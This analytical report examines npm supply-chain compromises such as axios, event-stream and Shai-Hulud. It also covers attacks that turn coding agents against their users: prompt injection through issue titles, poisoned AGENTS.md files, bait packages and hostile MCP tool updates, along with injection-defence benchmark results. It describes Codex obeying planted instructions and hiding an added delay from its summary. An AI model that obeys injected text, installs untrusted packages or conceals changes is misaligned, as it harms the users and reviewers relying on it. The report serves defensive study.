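The attackers began by deceiving Axios's lead maintainer, Jason Saayman, according to his post-mortem, which *Axios Supply-Chain Attack* (Solar Designer, 2026) quotes at length. About two weeks before the hostile releases, someone posing as a company's founder contacted him. The attackers had copied the founder's likeness and the company's branding. They invited Saayman to a convincing Slack workspace with what he presumes were fake staff profiles, and then to a Microsoft Teams meeting. During the meeting, he saw a message that something on his computer was out of date. He installed the supposed update, which was a remote-access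 trojan, a program that lets someone else control the computer. This gave the attackers his npm credentials.

Saayman had two-factor authentication switched on, and at first he couldn't explain how anyone had got in. But a second login factor offers little protection when the attacker controls a computer on which the owner has already logged in. Trusted Publishing didn't help either, because npm also accepted releases that bypassed it. Datadog Security Labs found from the registry's records that axios 1.14.0 had come through Trusted Publishing, while 1.14.1 came directly from Saayman's account.

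The attackers had prepared a second package called plain-crypto-js, a copy of a real encryption library with a similar name. They published a clean version on the morning of 30 March so that the package would have some history, then a version with an install script just before midnight UTC. They released axios 1.14.1 at 00:21 on 31 March and axios 0.30.4 at about 01:00. Together, they matched ranges such as `^1.14.0` and `^0.30.0`, so they reached users of both the current and the older series.

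The code of axios 1.14.1 was identical to that of 1.14.0. The attackers had changed only the manifest, where they added plain-crypto-js as a dependency. The rest happened during installation:

1. Someone installed axios, or a package that depends on it, without a lockfile that fixed an older version. npm chose 1.14.1.
2. npm read the new manifest and downloaded plain-crypto-js as well.
3. npm ran the install script in plain-crypto-js.
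4. The script identified the operating system, downloaded a trojan for macOS, Windows or Linux from the attackers' server, and started it.
5. The script deleted itself and replaced the package's manifest with a clean copy, so that anyone who looked later would find an ordinary encryption library.

No axios code ever imported plain-crypto-js, so programs that used axios carried on as normal.

The trojan was designed to send its operators a list of the files in the user's main folders, then contact them every 60 seconds for orders. The operators could run any command that the user's account could run. In Datadog's analysis, the trojan automatically sent only file listings and details of the machine, although Willison describes it as stealing credentials. Any theft of keys would have depended on what the operators did next, and the victim could not easily find out whether it had happened. Microsoft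 therefore told everyone who had installed either version to replace their credentials.

Bugs in the trojan limited the damage. The Linux version crashed in containers, the isolated environments where many build jobs run, but only after it had sent the file listings. According to Datadog's reading of the code, the Windows version did not start accepting commands on its first run. However, it downloaded itself again at each login, so the attackers could have supplied a working version later.

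The security company Huntress recorded the first infection on a customer's Mac 89 seconds after the release of axios 1.14.1, and counted at least 135 of its customers' machines contacting the attackers' server. Some infections came through OpenClaw, an open-source agent, and at least one came through a set of WordPress development tools that depended on axios. One automated scanner had flagged plain-crypto-js 16 minutes before the hostile axios release.

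Outsiders first detected the compromise at around 01:00, according to Saayman's timeline. eSentire's *examining the blast radius from the axios npm supply chain compromise* dates a public warning on social media to 01:46. When people reported the problem on the project's GitHub page, the attackers used Saayman's account to delete the reports. Another maintainer noticed but had fewer permissions than the stolen account, so he could not revoke its access or stop the attackers from undoing his repairs, and had to ask npm to step in. npm removed the releases at 03:15 according to the post-mortem, or at about 03:40 according to Datadog, so the exposure lasted roughly three hours.

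At 100 million downloads a week, axios averages about 1.8 million downloads every three hours. Many downloads in the three-hour period would have been of older versions, so the number of infected machines was probably much lower.

In *North Korea-Nexus Threat Actor Compromises Widely Used Axios NPM Package*, Larsen, Lenz and colleagues (2026) attribute the attack to a financially motivated group linked to North Korea. Microsoft also attributes the attack to a North Korean group, which it tracks under another name.

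OpenAI's *Our response to the Axios developer tool compromise* (2026) explains that one of the company's automated build jobs downloaded and ran the hostile version, axios 1.14.1. The job had access to the certificate that OpenAI uses to sign its Mac applications, which customers' computers check to verify that the software comes from OpenAI. A thief with this certificate could have made malware look like ChatGPT. OpenAI concluded from the order of events in the job that the attackers probably hadn't obtained the certificate, but it replaced the certificate anyway and required Mac users to update. It blamed a setting that referred to a build component by a movable label instead of an exact version, and the lack of a minimum age for new packages. A job that needs the certificate to sign applications doesn't have to install new code from the internet while it has that access.

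### Two attacks from 2018

Because the axios attackers ran their code on every machine at once, people noticed within the hour. The attack on event-stream was far more selective. In 2018 a stranger offered to help maintain this library for handling streams of data, and the original author, who no longer used it, handed over the publishing rights. On 9 September the new maintainer added a dependency called flatmap-stream, which was harmless at the time. A hostile version of flatmap-stream followed on 5 October. A developer raised the alarm on 20 November, about six and a half weeks later.

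The hostile code ran at import, but most of it was encrypted. The decryption key was the text description of Copay, a bitcoin wallet, so in any other program the decryption failed and nothing happened. When Copay's developers built their app, the code decrypted itself and altered another library included in the finished app. On customers' devices, when the app called the function that retrieves the wallet's keys, the altered library copied them if the balance was large enough. The attack therefore used the build machine's permission to write files, then the wallet's access to its owner's money.

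The hostile code called an outdated decryption function, which made Node.js print a warning. A developer discovered the code while looking for the cause of that warning, not through a stolen password or an install script.

The attack on eslint-scope in July 2018 lasted a few hours. ESLint checks JavaScript code for mistakes, and eslint-scope is one of its components. An attacker got into a maintainer's npm account with a password the maintainer had reused on other sites, then published a release with a malicious install script. The script fetched more code from a public text-sharing site and sent the attacker the user's npm settings file, which often contains a token for publishing packages. A bug in the script caused an error on some machines, and a user reported the error within about 40 minutes.

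npm later estimated that the attacker could have obtained tokens for about 4,500 accounts. People sometimes repeat this as the number of stolen credentials, but npm found no evidence that anyone had used them. It cancelled every token issued before the attack ended.

### Worms

Any of those 4,500 tokens could have let the attacker publish another hostile package and collect more tokens. Shai-Hulud, a family of worms that first appeared on npm in September 2025, automates this. Version 2.0, from November 2025, infected 796 packages. Its install script searched the machine for credentials and uploaded what it found to public GitHub repositories. If it found an npm token, the worm looked up the other packages the token's owner could publish, added itself to them and released new versions.

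Such a worm keeps growing as long as each infected maintainer's packages reach, on average, more than one other maintainer's token before somebody removes the packages. Install scripts are particularly useful for spreading it because maintainers install packages on the same machines they publish from. If the installation couldn't read a maintainer's publishing token, the worm could still steal other files but couldn't spread through that maintainer's packages.

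Shai-Hulud 2.0 also tried to delete the contents of the user's home directory if it couldn't find credentials it could use to spread or send out data. According to Mishcon de Reya, the hostile Tensorlake release monitored stolen GitHub tokens and could wipe the home directory if the owner cancelled one. A victim who follows the usual advice and cancels the token before cleaning the machine could therefore lose those files.

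A larger outbreak by number of packages came in August 2026. TechRadar's *New ChainDrop worm poisons over 1,300 npm packages* reports that attackers took over GitHub accounts connected to popular libraries, and that the security company Aikido found a Shai-Hulud variant in more than 1,300 packages. A day earlier, Underhill (2026), in *GitHub Account Breach Fuels Shai-Hulud npm Supply Chain Attack*, had reported hundreds of affected packages in what appears to be the same outbreak, so the count may have risen overnight. Other attacks in 2026 were larger by different measures, such as the Megalodon campaign, which ilSoftware.it says involved more than 5,500 GitHub repositories. Attackers have also combined a hostile release with injected text, as with the coding agent Cline.

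The number of compromised packages is a poor measure of harm. The Axios attack involved only two, the library itself and a package that existed only to carry the trojan, but Axios had far more users than most of the libraries a worm infects. Larsen and colleagues think the attacks of early 2026, including one on Python libraries, may have put hundreds of thousands of stolen secrets into circulation.

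### Updates that steal nothing

In January 2022 the developer Marak Squires sabotaged colors, his own library for printing coloured text in a terminal. There was no break-in. The new version printed garbage in an endless loop as soon as a program imported it. At the time, npm listed 18,971 packages that depended on colors directly, and another index counted at least 42,000 more that depended on it indirectly. Fresh installs of well-known tools, including Amazon's aws-cdk, stopped working immediately because the tools' manifests allowed the new version.

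Limits on files and network access would not have stopped this, because colors used only the processor and the terminal, which it needs to work. The users lost a working tool. If the invoice agent's date library did the same, the SSH keys would be safe, but the suppliers would not get paid until someone restored the old version. Projects with a lockfile that specified the old version would have avoided the problem.

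Accidents can do more damage than this sabotage did. In February 2018, npm released version 5.7.0 of its own package manager, which people update through npm like any other package. Linux users often ran it with `sudo`, which gives a program administrator rights. If they did this from an ordinary account, version 5.7.0 could change the ownership of system directories such as `/etc` and `/usr` to that account, and some servers stopped working. The company withdrew the change the next day in version 5.7.1.

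The bug was harmful because it ran with `sudo` rights. Without them, the kernel would have blocked the change of ownership of the system's files, and the bug would have produced an error message.

### Incidents compared

The table shows the time from the release of the hostile or faulty code to the first report of a problem. Removing the code usually took longer.

| Incident | Entry | When the code ran | Permissions used | Time to detection |
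|---|---|---|---|---|
| npm 5.7.0 (February 2018) | Mistake by npm's developers | When someone ran npm with `sudo` | Administrator's right to change file ownership | Within a day |
| eslint-scope (July 2018) | Reused password | Installation | Reading the user's npm settings; network | About 40 minutes |
| event-stream (2018) | Publishing rights given to a stranger | Import during Copay's build, then a call in the finished app | Writing files on the build machine; the wallet's access to its keys | About six and a half weeks |
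| colors (January 2022) | Sabotage by its own maintainer | Import | Terminal and processor | Almost at once |
| Shai-Hulud 2.0 (November 2025) | Stolen publishing tokens | Installation | Reading credentials, publishing packages, deleting files | Within hours |
| axios (March 2026) | Trojan on the maintainer's computer | Installation | Everything the installing account could do | About 40 minutes |
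| Tensorlake (October 2026) | Not established; linked to Shai-Hulud | Installation | Reading credentials, publishing packages, deleting files | About 11 minutes |

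## Attacks that combine injected text and packages

An agent with a shell can install a package, and a package can write files that an agent will later read. An attacker can therefore use injected text to get a hostile release installed, or use a hostile release to give instructions to a model.

### From an issue title to a release of Cline

Cline is an open-source coding agent with more than 5 million installations, according to its developers. On 21 December 2025, they added a workflow to the project's GitHub page that had a second agent, Claude, investigate and reply to each new issue (a public bug report or request). The workflow copied the issue's title into Claude's instructions, and Claude could run shell commands.

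In *Clinejection*, the security researcher Adnan Khan described how anyone with a GitHub account could have used this agent to reach Cline's publishing credentials. The attack would have gone through GitHub's cache, where workflows keep downloaded files to save time on later runs.

| Step | Permission that made it possible |
|---|---|
| A stranger's text reaches the agent | Any GitHub user could open an issue and start the workflow |
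| The agent installs a package named in the title, and its install script runs | The agent had a shell |
| The script replaces files in the cache | Every workflow on the project's main branch shared one cache |
| The nightly release job runs the replaced files | The job loaded its libraries from that cache |
| The files copy the publishing credentials | The job held those credentials |
| The attacker publishes an ordinary release | The nightly credentials also worked for ordinary releases |

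The developers had limited the workflow's GitHub token so that Claude could read the code and write to issues but not change the code. In Miller and Shapiro's terms, Claude had little permission over the project but much more authority, because the release job would run whatever was in the cache. *Post-mortem*, Cline's own account (Rizwan, 2026), describes a shell in this position as "functionally equivalent to giving every GitHub user shell access".

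Removing any one of the permissions in the table would have blocked this route to an ordinary release. Khan recommended limiting the agent to reading files and running the few GitHub commands it needed, keeping the cache out of release jobs, and publishing nightly versions under a separate name with separate credentials. Even without the cache, some risk would have remained because the shell could also read the key that the workflow used to access and pay for Claude.

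### What Khan showed and what the intruder did

Khan tested only the beginning of the chain, using a copy of Cline's repository and his own Claude account. Claude Opus 4.5 ran the install command in every attempt, though he doesn't say how many he made. He worked out the later steps from Cline's public workflow files and his own tool, which he had used to demonstrate similar flaws elsewhere. He did not attack Cline's real release job.

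He reported the flaw on 1 January 2026, tried several more times to reach the company, and published his findings on 9 February. Cline removed the vulnerable workflows within 30 minutes.

Someone else had probably broken in by then. Cline's nightly release jobs had failed between 31 January and 3 February, and the failures matched the traces left by Khan's publicly available tool. On 10 February, an anonymous sender told Khan that they had working credentials for publishing Cline on npm and on OpenVSX, a marketplace for editor extensions. Cline replied the next day that it had replaced all its publishing credentials.

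It had in fact deleted the wrong npm token. According to Rizwan, the staff had checked a management page that showed no active tokens, but that page didn't list the exposed one. On 17 February, somebody used the exposed token to publish cline@2.3.0.

The evidence doesn't prove that the attack followed the chain Khan described, although The Hacker News writes that it "is exactly what happened". The intruder had a valid token, and the failed jobs suggest that someone had tampered with the cache. But Khan only presumes that the intruder used the same flaw. He calls the issue agent the most obvious way in but doesn't claim to know that the intruder used it. Neither he nor Cline has identified an issue title that started the attack, and nobody has publicly identified the intruder.

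The new release contained the same program as the previous one, plus an install script that added OpenClaw, a legitimate agent. The security company StepSecurity counted about 4,000 downloads in the eight hours before Cline withdrew support for the release. Henrik Plate of Endor Labs, another security company, considered the impact low because the script did not start OpenClaw's background service. The incident's entry in the OSV database, *GHSA-9ppg-jx86-fqw7* (2026), also lists its severity as low.

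That rating reflects what the intruder chose to install, and a different install script could have read users' SSH keys. Cline has since moved its npm releases to short-lived credentials and says any future agent of this kind will have read-only access and no shell.

### When an agent chooses the package

The attack on Cline would have needed an instruction in the issue title. An attacker can also publish a package that looks suitable and wait for an agent to choose it.

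*Claude adds malware to crypto agent* (Pezo, 2026) describes a campaign that the security company ReversingLabs named PromptMink. On 28 February 2026, a commit (a recorded change to a project's code) added a hostile package to openpaw-graveyard, an agent that trades cryptocurrency. The commit listed Claude Opus as a co-author, but that does not establish whether the model or the human developer chose the package. Pezo also shows no injected instruction.

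The attackers used two layers of packages. The commit added a package with useful functions for cryptocurrency projects and no hostile code of its own. That package depended on a second one, disguised as a data-checking tool, which collected settings files, where developers often keep passwords and wallet keys. When npm removed an earlier version of the second package in October 2025, the attackers published the same code under a new name that day and made the first package depend on it. They could therefore replace the malicious package while the first one kept its reputation.

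Pezo attributes the campaign to Famous Chollima, a group linked to North Korea, and counts 60 packages over seven months. He thinks the attackers were targeting coding agents, partly because they wrote documentation that heavily advertised each package's usefulness. He also describes a bot that reported using the bait package because it had a function the bot needed.

These cases make the theory plausible, but two known users are weak evidence for Pezo's claim that the packages fooled agents more successfully than people. In either case, the attack depended on permission to add a dependency without a separate check, and then on the trading agent's access to its own secrets. Searching the documentation for hostile instructions would not have helped if it only praised the package.

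### From a library to the agent's instructions

Coding agents look for project files that tell them how to work, such as AGENTS.md. A developer might use this file to specify how to name variables or run tests. The agent treats the file's contents as instructions from the project, but other programs may be able to write to it.

NVIDIA's *Mitigating Indirect AGENTS.md Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (April 2026) describes a hostile library that the company's security testers wrote in Go. They added it to a tiny program that printed a greeting, then asked OpenAI's coding agent Codex to change the greeting. When Codex built the program, the library's code ran, detected Codex's working environment and wrote a new AGENTS.md. The code would have done nothing unusual on an ordinary developer's machine.

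The new file contained instructions for Codex to add a five-minute delay to the program, ignore the user's request, and leave the delay out of its reports. Codex complied and also added a comment asking other models not to mention the delay. The summary of the proposed change omitted the delay. The resulting program still printed the old greeting.

The library could write the file because its code had the same file access as the build. Codex then used its own permission to add a harmless delay to the program and propose the change to the project. NVIDIA demonstrated the method in one constructed case and did not measure how often it works.

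NVIDIA reported the problem to OpenAI on 1 July 2025. On 19 August, OpenAI concluded that the attack did not significantly increase the risk beyond what a compromised dependency already poses, and planned no changes. NVIDIA calls this "a fair assessment".

For this experiment, OpenAI's reply is largely right, because the library's code already ran where Codex was working and could have added the delay itself. Using Codex still helped the attacker in some ways, since the model can fit a change to a project the attacker has never seen and writes the summary that a busy reviewer may read instead of the code. A direct edit by the library might have entered the same proposal, but Codex could have noticed and mentioned a change it had not made.

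The reply assumes that the library and the agent have the same permissions, A(c) = A(P), which is the default, so it is less convincing when the library is limited. Suppose a developer confines a library to the project's folder while the agent keeps its shell and network access. The library can no longer read an SSH key, but it can write a file with instructions for the agent to read the key. In the earlier notation, the agent's help belongs to R(c). The confinement then holds only if the library cannot write instruction files, or if the agent also lacks the permissions denied to the library. NVIDIA recommends protecting instruction files.

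A library that cannot write files may still be able to supply text. If the invoice agent puts the date library's output into the model's context, a hostile version of the library could return an instruction instead of a date, and the model might follow it using the shell. The agent can prevent this by rejecting any output that isn't a valid date.

An attack can begin before any of the attacker's code has run. Researchers at the AI Now Institute got Claude Code and Codex to run a malicious program that came with a library, although the library never called it and the user had only asked for a security review. OpenAI's argument does not cover this case, because the agent gave the attacker the ability to run code.

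A library's own maintainer can also use text against agents. The maintainer of jqwik, a Java testing library, added an instruction telling coding agents to delete its tests and code. Claude Code detected the instruction and stopped, but some other agents did not.

Two waves of worms in May and June 2026, Mini Shai-Hulud and Miasma, used the configuration files of coding assistants such as Claude Code, Gemini CLI and Cursor. SC Media's *AI agents breach production systems, spread malware in major exploits* reports that Mini Shai-Hulud compromised more than 170 packages. Real attackers have therefore gone from packages to agents' settings. But the assistant's software directly runs commands in some configuration files, so these worms are not clear evidence that a model obeyed injected text.

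### Tools and skills are dependencies too

Developers often connect agents to outside tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for offering tools to a model. An MCP server is a program that provides one or more tools. It may run on the user's machine or on its publisher's. For each tool, the server supplies a name, a description and a list of the inputs the tool accepts. This text enters the model's context so that the model can decide when to use the tool.

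A local MCP server is a dependency whose code runs with the user's permissions, and any MCP server can also supply hostile text. A skill gives an agent written instructions, and sometimes scripts, for a particular task. A hostile skill may not need its own code if the agent has a shell.

Agents sometimes choose these tools themselves. Help Net Security's *AI coding agents are installing MCP servers that will never be patched* (2026) describes sessions in which coding agents installed or suggested servers whose developers had abandoned them. In 98% of these sessions, the agent appeared to have recalled the server's name from the model's training data. Glow, the security company that did the research, examined only sessions in which an abandoned server appeared, so the figure doesn't show how often agents choose one. In one session, the agent looked up the package, received a notice that it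 was deprecated, and installed it without telling the user.

One of the abandoned servers lets an agent control a web browser. A flaw in the server could let injected text start any program on the machine, even though the developer had approved only browsing. Glow had seen no attacker use the flaw. The agent had started these servers with a command that downloads and immediately runs a package, so they never appeared in the project's list of dependencies, and a company that checks only such lists would miss them.

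Whether a publisher's later changes reach existing users automatically depends on the type of tool. Some agents fetch the newest version of an MCP server every time they load it, according to Help Net Security's *One in four MCP servers opens AI agent security to code execution* (2026), which draws on research by the security company Noma. Skills are usually fixed files that the user must update by hand.

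TechRadar's *Experts warn malicious AI skills are hitting more victims than ever* reports a case found by the security company Zenity. Attackers copied existing skills, published them under similar names, and left them harmless while their download counts grew. They then added instructions to steal SSH keys, cloud credentials and publishing tokens. One family of these skills had more than 1.7 million installations. That total includes repeat installations and probably many from before the attackers added the instructions, so it is not a count of victims.

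An approval can also cover more than the user intended. Infosecurity Magazine's *MCP Is Creating Major Governance Gaps, Researchers Warn* describes a test by OX Security, which sells security products. A hostile MCP server requested a harmless file from Claude Code, and the user chose "always allow". The server then requested a settings file containing secrets, and Claude Code sent it without asking the user again. Anthropic replied that this was the documented behaviour of "always allow", and that the model's ability to spot hostile content was not a security boundary.

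OX used Claude Haiku 3.5, an old model. A newer one might refuse the second request more often, but the approval would still permit it.

### A test of hostile tool updates

In *Beyond Prompt Injection*, Kan, Luo and colleagues (2026) tested whether agents would keep trusting a tool after its code changed. They wrote two versions of a tool for tidying text, one harmless and one hostile, with the same name, description and normal output. Once an agent had accepted the harmless version, they replaced it with the hostile one.

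While tidying the text, the hostile version also tried to do one of three things: send a file of fake credentials to a test server, place an order through a test service, or overwrite a research note. The researchers ran the experiment in seven agent programs, including Claude Code, Codex CLI and Gemini CLI. Each combination of program and goal had 100 planned tasks, for 2,100 in total.

For comparison, the researchers tested another update that left the tool's code alone but changed its description to include a request for the model to make an extra tool call. They also presented each kind of hostile version at first installation, when a code scanner reviewed it. They had added the scanner themselves because the agent programs do not run one by default. The table gives the share of tasks in which the attacker achieved their goal.

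| When the hostile version arrived | Hostile code | Hostile description |
|---|---|---|
| First installation, with a review | 0% | 2.9% |
| Later update, without a review | 99.9% | 20.2% |

Kan and colleagues give the highest success rate as 100.0%, but their results for the individual programs add up to 2,098 of 2,100 tasks. The agents also returned the correct tidied text in 99.6% of tasks, so a user would rarely have noticed a problem. The success rate was somewhat lower in further tests, averaging 96.4% across different models, and the paper's overall figure is 97.6%.

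The hostile code succeeded so often because it ran whenever the model called the tool. A hostile description works only if the model also decides to make the extra call, and the surrounding program seems to affect that decision. The same model, GLM-5.3-Flash, made extra calls in 297 of 300 tasks in Claude Code and in none of 300 in OpenCode. These results are weak evidence of how Anthropic's own models would behave in Claude Code.

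The 20.2% figure also understates the damage from changed descriptions. In the tests with the research note, 42.4% of tasks overwrote the file, but only 14.4% wrote the exact text the attacker wanted. Kan and colleagues counted only the exact matches as successes, although the owner would have lost the original note either way.

All seven programs applied an old approval to new code. This finding is more useful than the rate near 100%, which is unsurprising when the researchers write the tool, control the update and leave the necessary permissions in place. Kan and colleagues recommend tying each approval to the exact code reviewed, so any change requires a new decision. They also recommend limiting what a tool can do while it runs, because an approved version may still be malicious. They did not test such limits, but a tool that only tidies text doesn't need to read credentials, place orders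 or overwrite a research note.

### OX Security's survey

OX Security analysed 542,207 open-source components between July and October 2026, including npm and Python packages, MCP servers and skills. Infosecurity Magazine reports that 22% of the MCP servers OX flagged as suspicious contained prompt injection or hostile tool descriptions, and 16% ran code during installation or import. Of the flagged skills, 26% contained prompt injection or hostile tool descriptions, 0% ran code during installation or import, and 44% contained instructions to send data out. These figures come from a vendor and depend on what its scanner flags as suspicious.

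OX also found that 82% were malicious in the first version it observed, which may not be the first version published. The percentage apparently refers to flagged MCP servers, because 82% of all components in the survey would mean about 445,000 malicious ones.

If the figure is right for flagged servers, at most 18% began with a clean version and became malicious later. A check at first installation could then catch most malicious servers, and the kind of update that Kan and colleagues studied would be less common. But the survey counts components rather than users, and a popular server that becomes malicious after a year could harm more people than hundreds of servers that few people install.

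OX found that 67% of the MCP servers ran on machines controlled by their publishers. A user cannot inspect the code on such a machine or pin its version with a lockfile, and the publisher can change the code between calls. The user can still limit which data the agent sends to the server and which other tools the agent can use after reading the server's reply.

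## Why screening text and packages leaves a gap

A company can try to stop both kinds of attack before they can use the agent's permissions, by checking text before the model acts on it and packages before anyone installs them. Both kinds of checking have improved but still miss some attacks. An attack that gets through can use every permission it would have had without the check.

### How developers screen text

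An injection classifier is a program, often a small machine-learning model, that estimates how likely a piece of text is to contain an attack. If the estimate is above a threshold, the agent's program can remove the text, stop the task or warn the user. The Frontier Model Forum's *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026), a brief from an industry body, describes classifiers that check the model's input, its output, or its activations, which are the numbers it computes while processing text. Developers train these classifiers on known injections.

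Anthropic uses classifiers it calls probes to inspect tool results before the model acts on them. In some products, a setting called auto mode adds another classifier to block tool calls that look dangerous. With auto mode on, an attack has to get past both checks.

Developers also train the model to ignore injected instructions. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) describes adversarial training, in which an automated attacker called GPT-Red writes injections and the model learns to resist them while still completing legitimate tasks. The trained model usually resists injections, but it can fail on text unlike its training data.

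One reason for the gap is that models judge where text came from partly by its style. Willison (2026) summarises *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, in which Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell wrote hostile text in the style of a model's own reasoning. Models often treated this text as their own reasoning, even when the markers around it indicated otherwise. When the researchers changed the style but kept the meaning, the attack's average success rate fell from 61% to 10%. Willison's example is a user overriding safety training, which differs from an attack through a hostile email, but both work when the model is wrong about who wrote the text.

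A classifier that sees only the text also can't tell whether "Please use our new bank account from this month" came from a real supplier or a thief. Siu and colleagues argue that a defence has to check whether the agent is pursuing an authorised goal, whether the action serves that goal, whether the instruction came from an authorised source, and whether data stays where it is allowed to go. The sentence about the bank account contains none of this information, so such a classifier will either block real changes of account or let false ones through.

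### How developers screen packages

A malware scanner may examine a package's files for suspicious features, such as an install script or scrambled code. It may also run the package in an isolated environment and record what it does. The install script in the axios attack had an obvious warning sign. Datadog Security Labs found that the attackers had scrambled all its text, including file names and commands.

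*An Empirical Study of Observability Limits in Advanced Software Supply Chain Attacks* (Tan, Brierley and colleagues, 2026) examined records of 16,272 malicious packages. Of the packages with a recorded trigger, 96% ran their hostile code during installation. Of the 6,443 with a recorded method of evading detection, 6,360 used encoding or scrambling. But the collection contains only packages that somebody caught, so it probably overstates how easy hostile code is to recognise. The code in event-stream decrypted itself only inside one bitcoin wallet, and NVIDIA's test library acted only when Codex was present. A scanner that ran either of them in an ordinary test environment would have detected nothing hostile.

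Other tools block packages that somebody has already identified as malicious. Datadog's Supply-Chain Firewall does this when a developer installs a package with npm or its Python equivalent, pip. It can't recognise a malicious package that an attacker has just published and nobody has reported yet.

A person can review the changes between two versions, but reading every change is unrealistic for a project with 1,700 packages. To catch the problem in axios 1.14.1, a reviewer would have had to follow the new line in the manifest to plain-crypto-js and notice its install script. Another warning sign was that the maintainer's email address in the registry had changed since the previous release. A program can easily check for that, though maintainers also change their addresses for ordinary reasons.

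Pinning exact versions, as a lockfile does for all of a program's dependencies, prevents unexpected changes. But if a pinned version is already malicious, every installation will include it. The program also keeps any security flaws in the old version until someone updates the pin, and then the team needs another way to judge whether the new release is safe.

With a waiting period, the installer rejects any release younger than a certain age, such as one day, in the hope that someone else will discover an attack in the meantime. OpenAI's build job had no such rule when it installed the malicious version of axios.

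Companies can also monitor what a package does after installation. Tan and colleagues ran seven simulated attacks and recorded them in 11 types of log and other monitoring data. The best single type recovered less than 40% of the steps they expected to find. Combining two complementary types improved this by a factor of about 1.6, but the gain depended on which two. One suspicious step is enough to raise an alarm, so a company can detect an attack even when most of its steps are missing from the data. The missing steps matter more afterwards, when the company has to work out which credentials the intruder took.

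### Success rates on fixed attacks

A success rate for prompt injection means little without knowing how many attempts the attacker had and whether the attacker could change the attack after seeing it fail.

The security company Gray Swan maintains a benchmark of attacks from a public competition. The attacks try to make agents do things such as leak private data, destroy files or transfer money. Anthropic's July 2026 system card for Claude Opus 5, a report on the model's testing, gives results for 1,130 attacks that had worked well across several models. In September, OpenAI reported results for a set of 1,810. The table shows the chance that at least one of 15 attempts succeeds.

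| Model | Attack set | Success within 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 1,130 attacks | 2.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 1,130 attacks | 5.5% |
| Muse Spark (Meta) | 1,130 attacks | 16.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol (OpenAI) | 1,130 attacks | 20.0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol (OpenAI) | 1,810 attacks | 27.0% |
| GPT-6 Astra (OpenAI) | 1,810 attacks | 8.5% |

With a single attempt, the rate was 0.2% for Opus 5 and 3.1% for GPT-5.6 Sol. Sol did worse on the larger set, so Astra's 8.5% isn't directly comparable with the 2.0% for Opus 5. The comparison is also limited because OpenAI tested Astra with safeguards on, while Anthropic tested its own models without additional ones. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Mythos 5.1, from September, describes that model as the company's most robust yet on this benchmark.

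The attacker had several attempts in these tests but could not adapt, because the attacks already existed. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr et al., October 2025) found that stronger attacks that adapt to a prompt injection defence can get past it. Anthropic cites the paper when warning that fixed tests can give a false sense of security.

### Success rates when attackers can adapt

Anthropic therefore also tests with attackers who refine their attacks. For coding and computer use (operating a graphical interface as a person would with a mouse and keyboard), it uses Shade, an automated attacker from Gray Swan. For browsing, it uses attacks by professional testers. The results below are for Opus 5 with extended thinking, a setting in which the model reasons at length before acting.

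| Task | Attempts per scenario | Successful attempts | Scenarios with a success | With added safeguards |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Coding | 200 | 0.56% | 13 of 40 | 0.18%, in 4 of 40 |
| Computer use | 200 | 0.54% | 1 of 14 | 0.25%, in 1 of 14 |
| Browsing | 10 | 3.70% | 11 of 129 | 0%, in 0 of 129 |

The previous model, Opus 4.8, did much worse without the safeguards. Attackers succeeded in 7.03% of attempts in coding, 7.14% in computer use and 31.5% in browsing.

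These figures could be too high or too low for a real company. The attackers had many attempts at a known scenario, while a real attacker usually knows less about the target and risks discovery with each attempt. But the coding attacker had learned from earlier models before Anthropic used it on Opus 5, and an attacker who practised on Opus 5 itself might do better.

Older results show how much an attack success rate depends on the attacker. VentureBeat reports that in February 2026, all 200 attempts against Claude Opus 4.6 in a coding test failed. A few months later, attacks on the newer Opus 4.8 succeeded in 23 of 40 coding scenarios. Either the newer model was weaker or the attacks had improved, and a 0% success rate could mean that the model is secure or that the attacks were weak. In a graphical interface, attacks on Opus 4.6 succeeded 78.6% of the time by the 200th attempt, while attacks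 on Opus 5 succeeded in one of 14 scenarios, or about 7%. That looks like a large improvement if the tests were similar.

In OpenAI's internal tests, the share of indirect attacks that its models resisted rose from 96.23% for GPT-5.6 Sol to 99.79% for Astra. But the attacks came from GPT-Red, the approach OpenAI also uses in training, so Astra had already been trained against attacks of this kind. The 8.5% on Gray Swan's attacks is probably a better guide to attacks that OpenAI did not design.

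### Outside tests of current agents

Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to attack coding agents with scenarios Anthropic had not seen. Willison reports that all 720 attempts against three Anthropic models in auto mode failed. If the attempts were independent, all 720 would still fail about one time in 20 at a true success rate of about 0.4%. The result therefore supports a low success rate, at least for attacks like these.

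A public challenge tested a setup more like the invoice agent's. Fernando Irarrázaval gave an OpenClaw assistant some secrets and invited people to steal them by email. About 2,000 people made some 6,000 attempts, and nobody succeeded. The assistant ran on the older Opus 4.6, with instructions never to reveal credentials or run commands because of an email. Willison accepts that training has made such attacks much harder. He still advises against using an agent where an injection could do irreversible damage, because a more skilled attacker might succeed.

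In August 2026, the security researcher Johann Rehberger reported an attack on Claude Code, running Opus 5 in auto mode, that he said worked 80% of the time. The agent ran hostile code among files it had downloaded without following any instruction from the attacker, so a test that counts only obeyed instructions would miss the attack. In a few runs, the agent noticed the hostile program and tried to stop it, but auto mode blocked its command. The 80% is his own figure for one attack, so it doesn't contradict the Trajectory Labs result.

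Screening text can also miss a compromised update, because the command that installs it can be the same one the agent normally runs. When Anthropic introduced auto mode in March 2026, the default rules allowed an agent to install any package already listed in a project's manifest. Willison pointed out that this would let through a hostile new version of a listed library.

### The chance of one success in many attempts

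The earlier formula for the risk from many packages, 1 − (1 − p)ⁿ, also applies to n injection attempts if they are independent and each succeeds with probability p. With p = 1% and n = 100, the chance of at least one success is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%. After 500 attempts it is more than 99%. The calculation assumes that p stays the same and that nobody blocks the sender after noticing the failed attempts.

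The weakest assumption is that attack attempts succeed or fail independently. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* gives attack success rates for that older model of 4.7% after one attempt, 33.6% after ten and 63% after 100. If the attempts were independent, the rates would have been about 38% after ten and 99% after 100. The actual rate rises more slowly because some tasks are much harder to attack than others.

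The computer-use test of Opus 5 is a more extreme case. Attackers succeeded in 0.54% of 2,800 attempts, or about 15 times. All of these successes came from one of the 14 scenarios, where about 7.5% of attempts worked. An attacker could therefore send thousands of emails to a company whose setup resembles one of the other 13 scenarios and get nothing, while a company with the weak setup might lose its data after a dozen or so.

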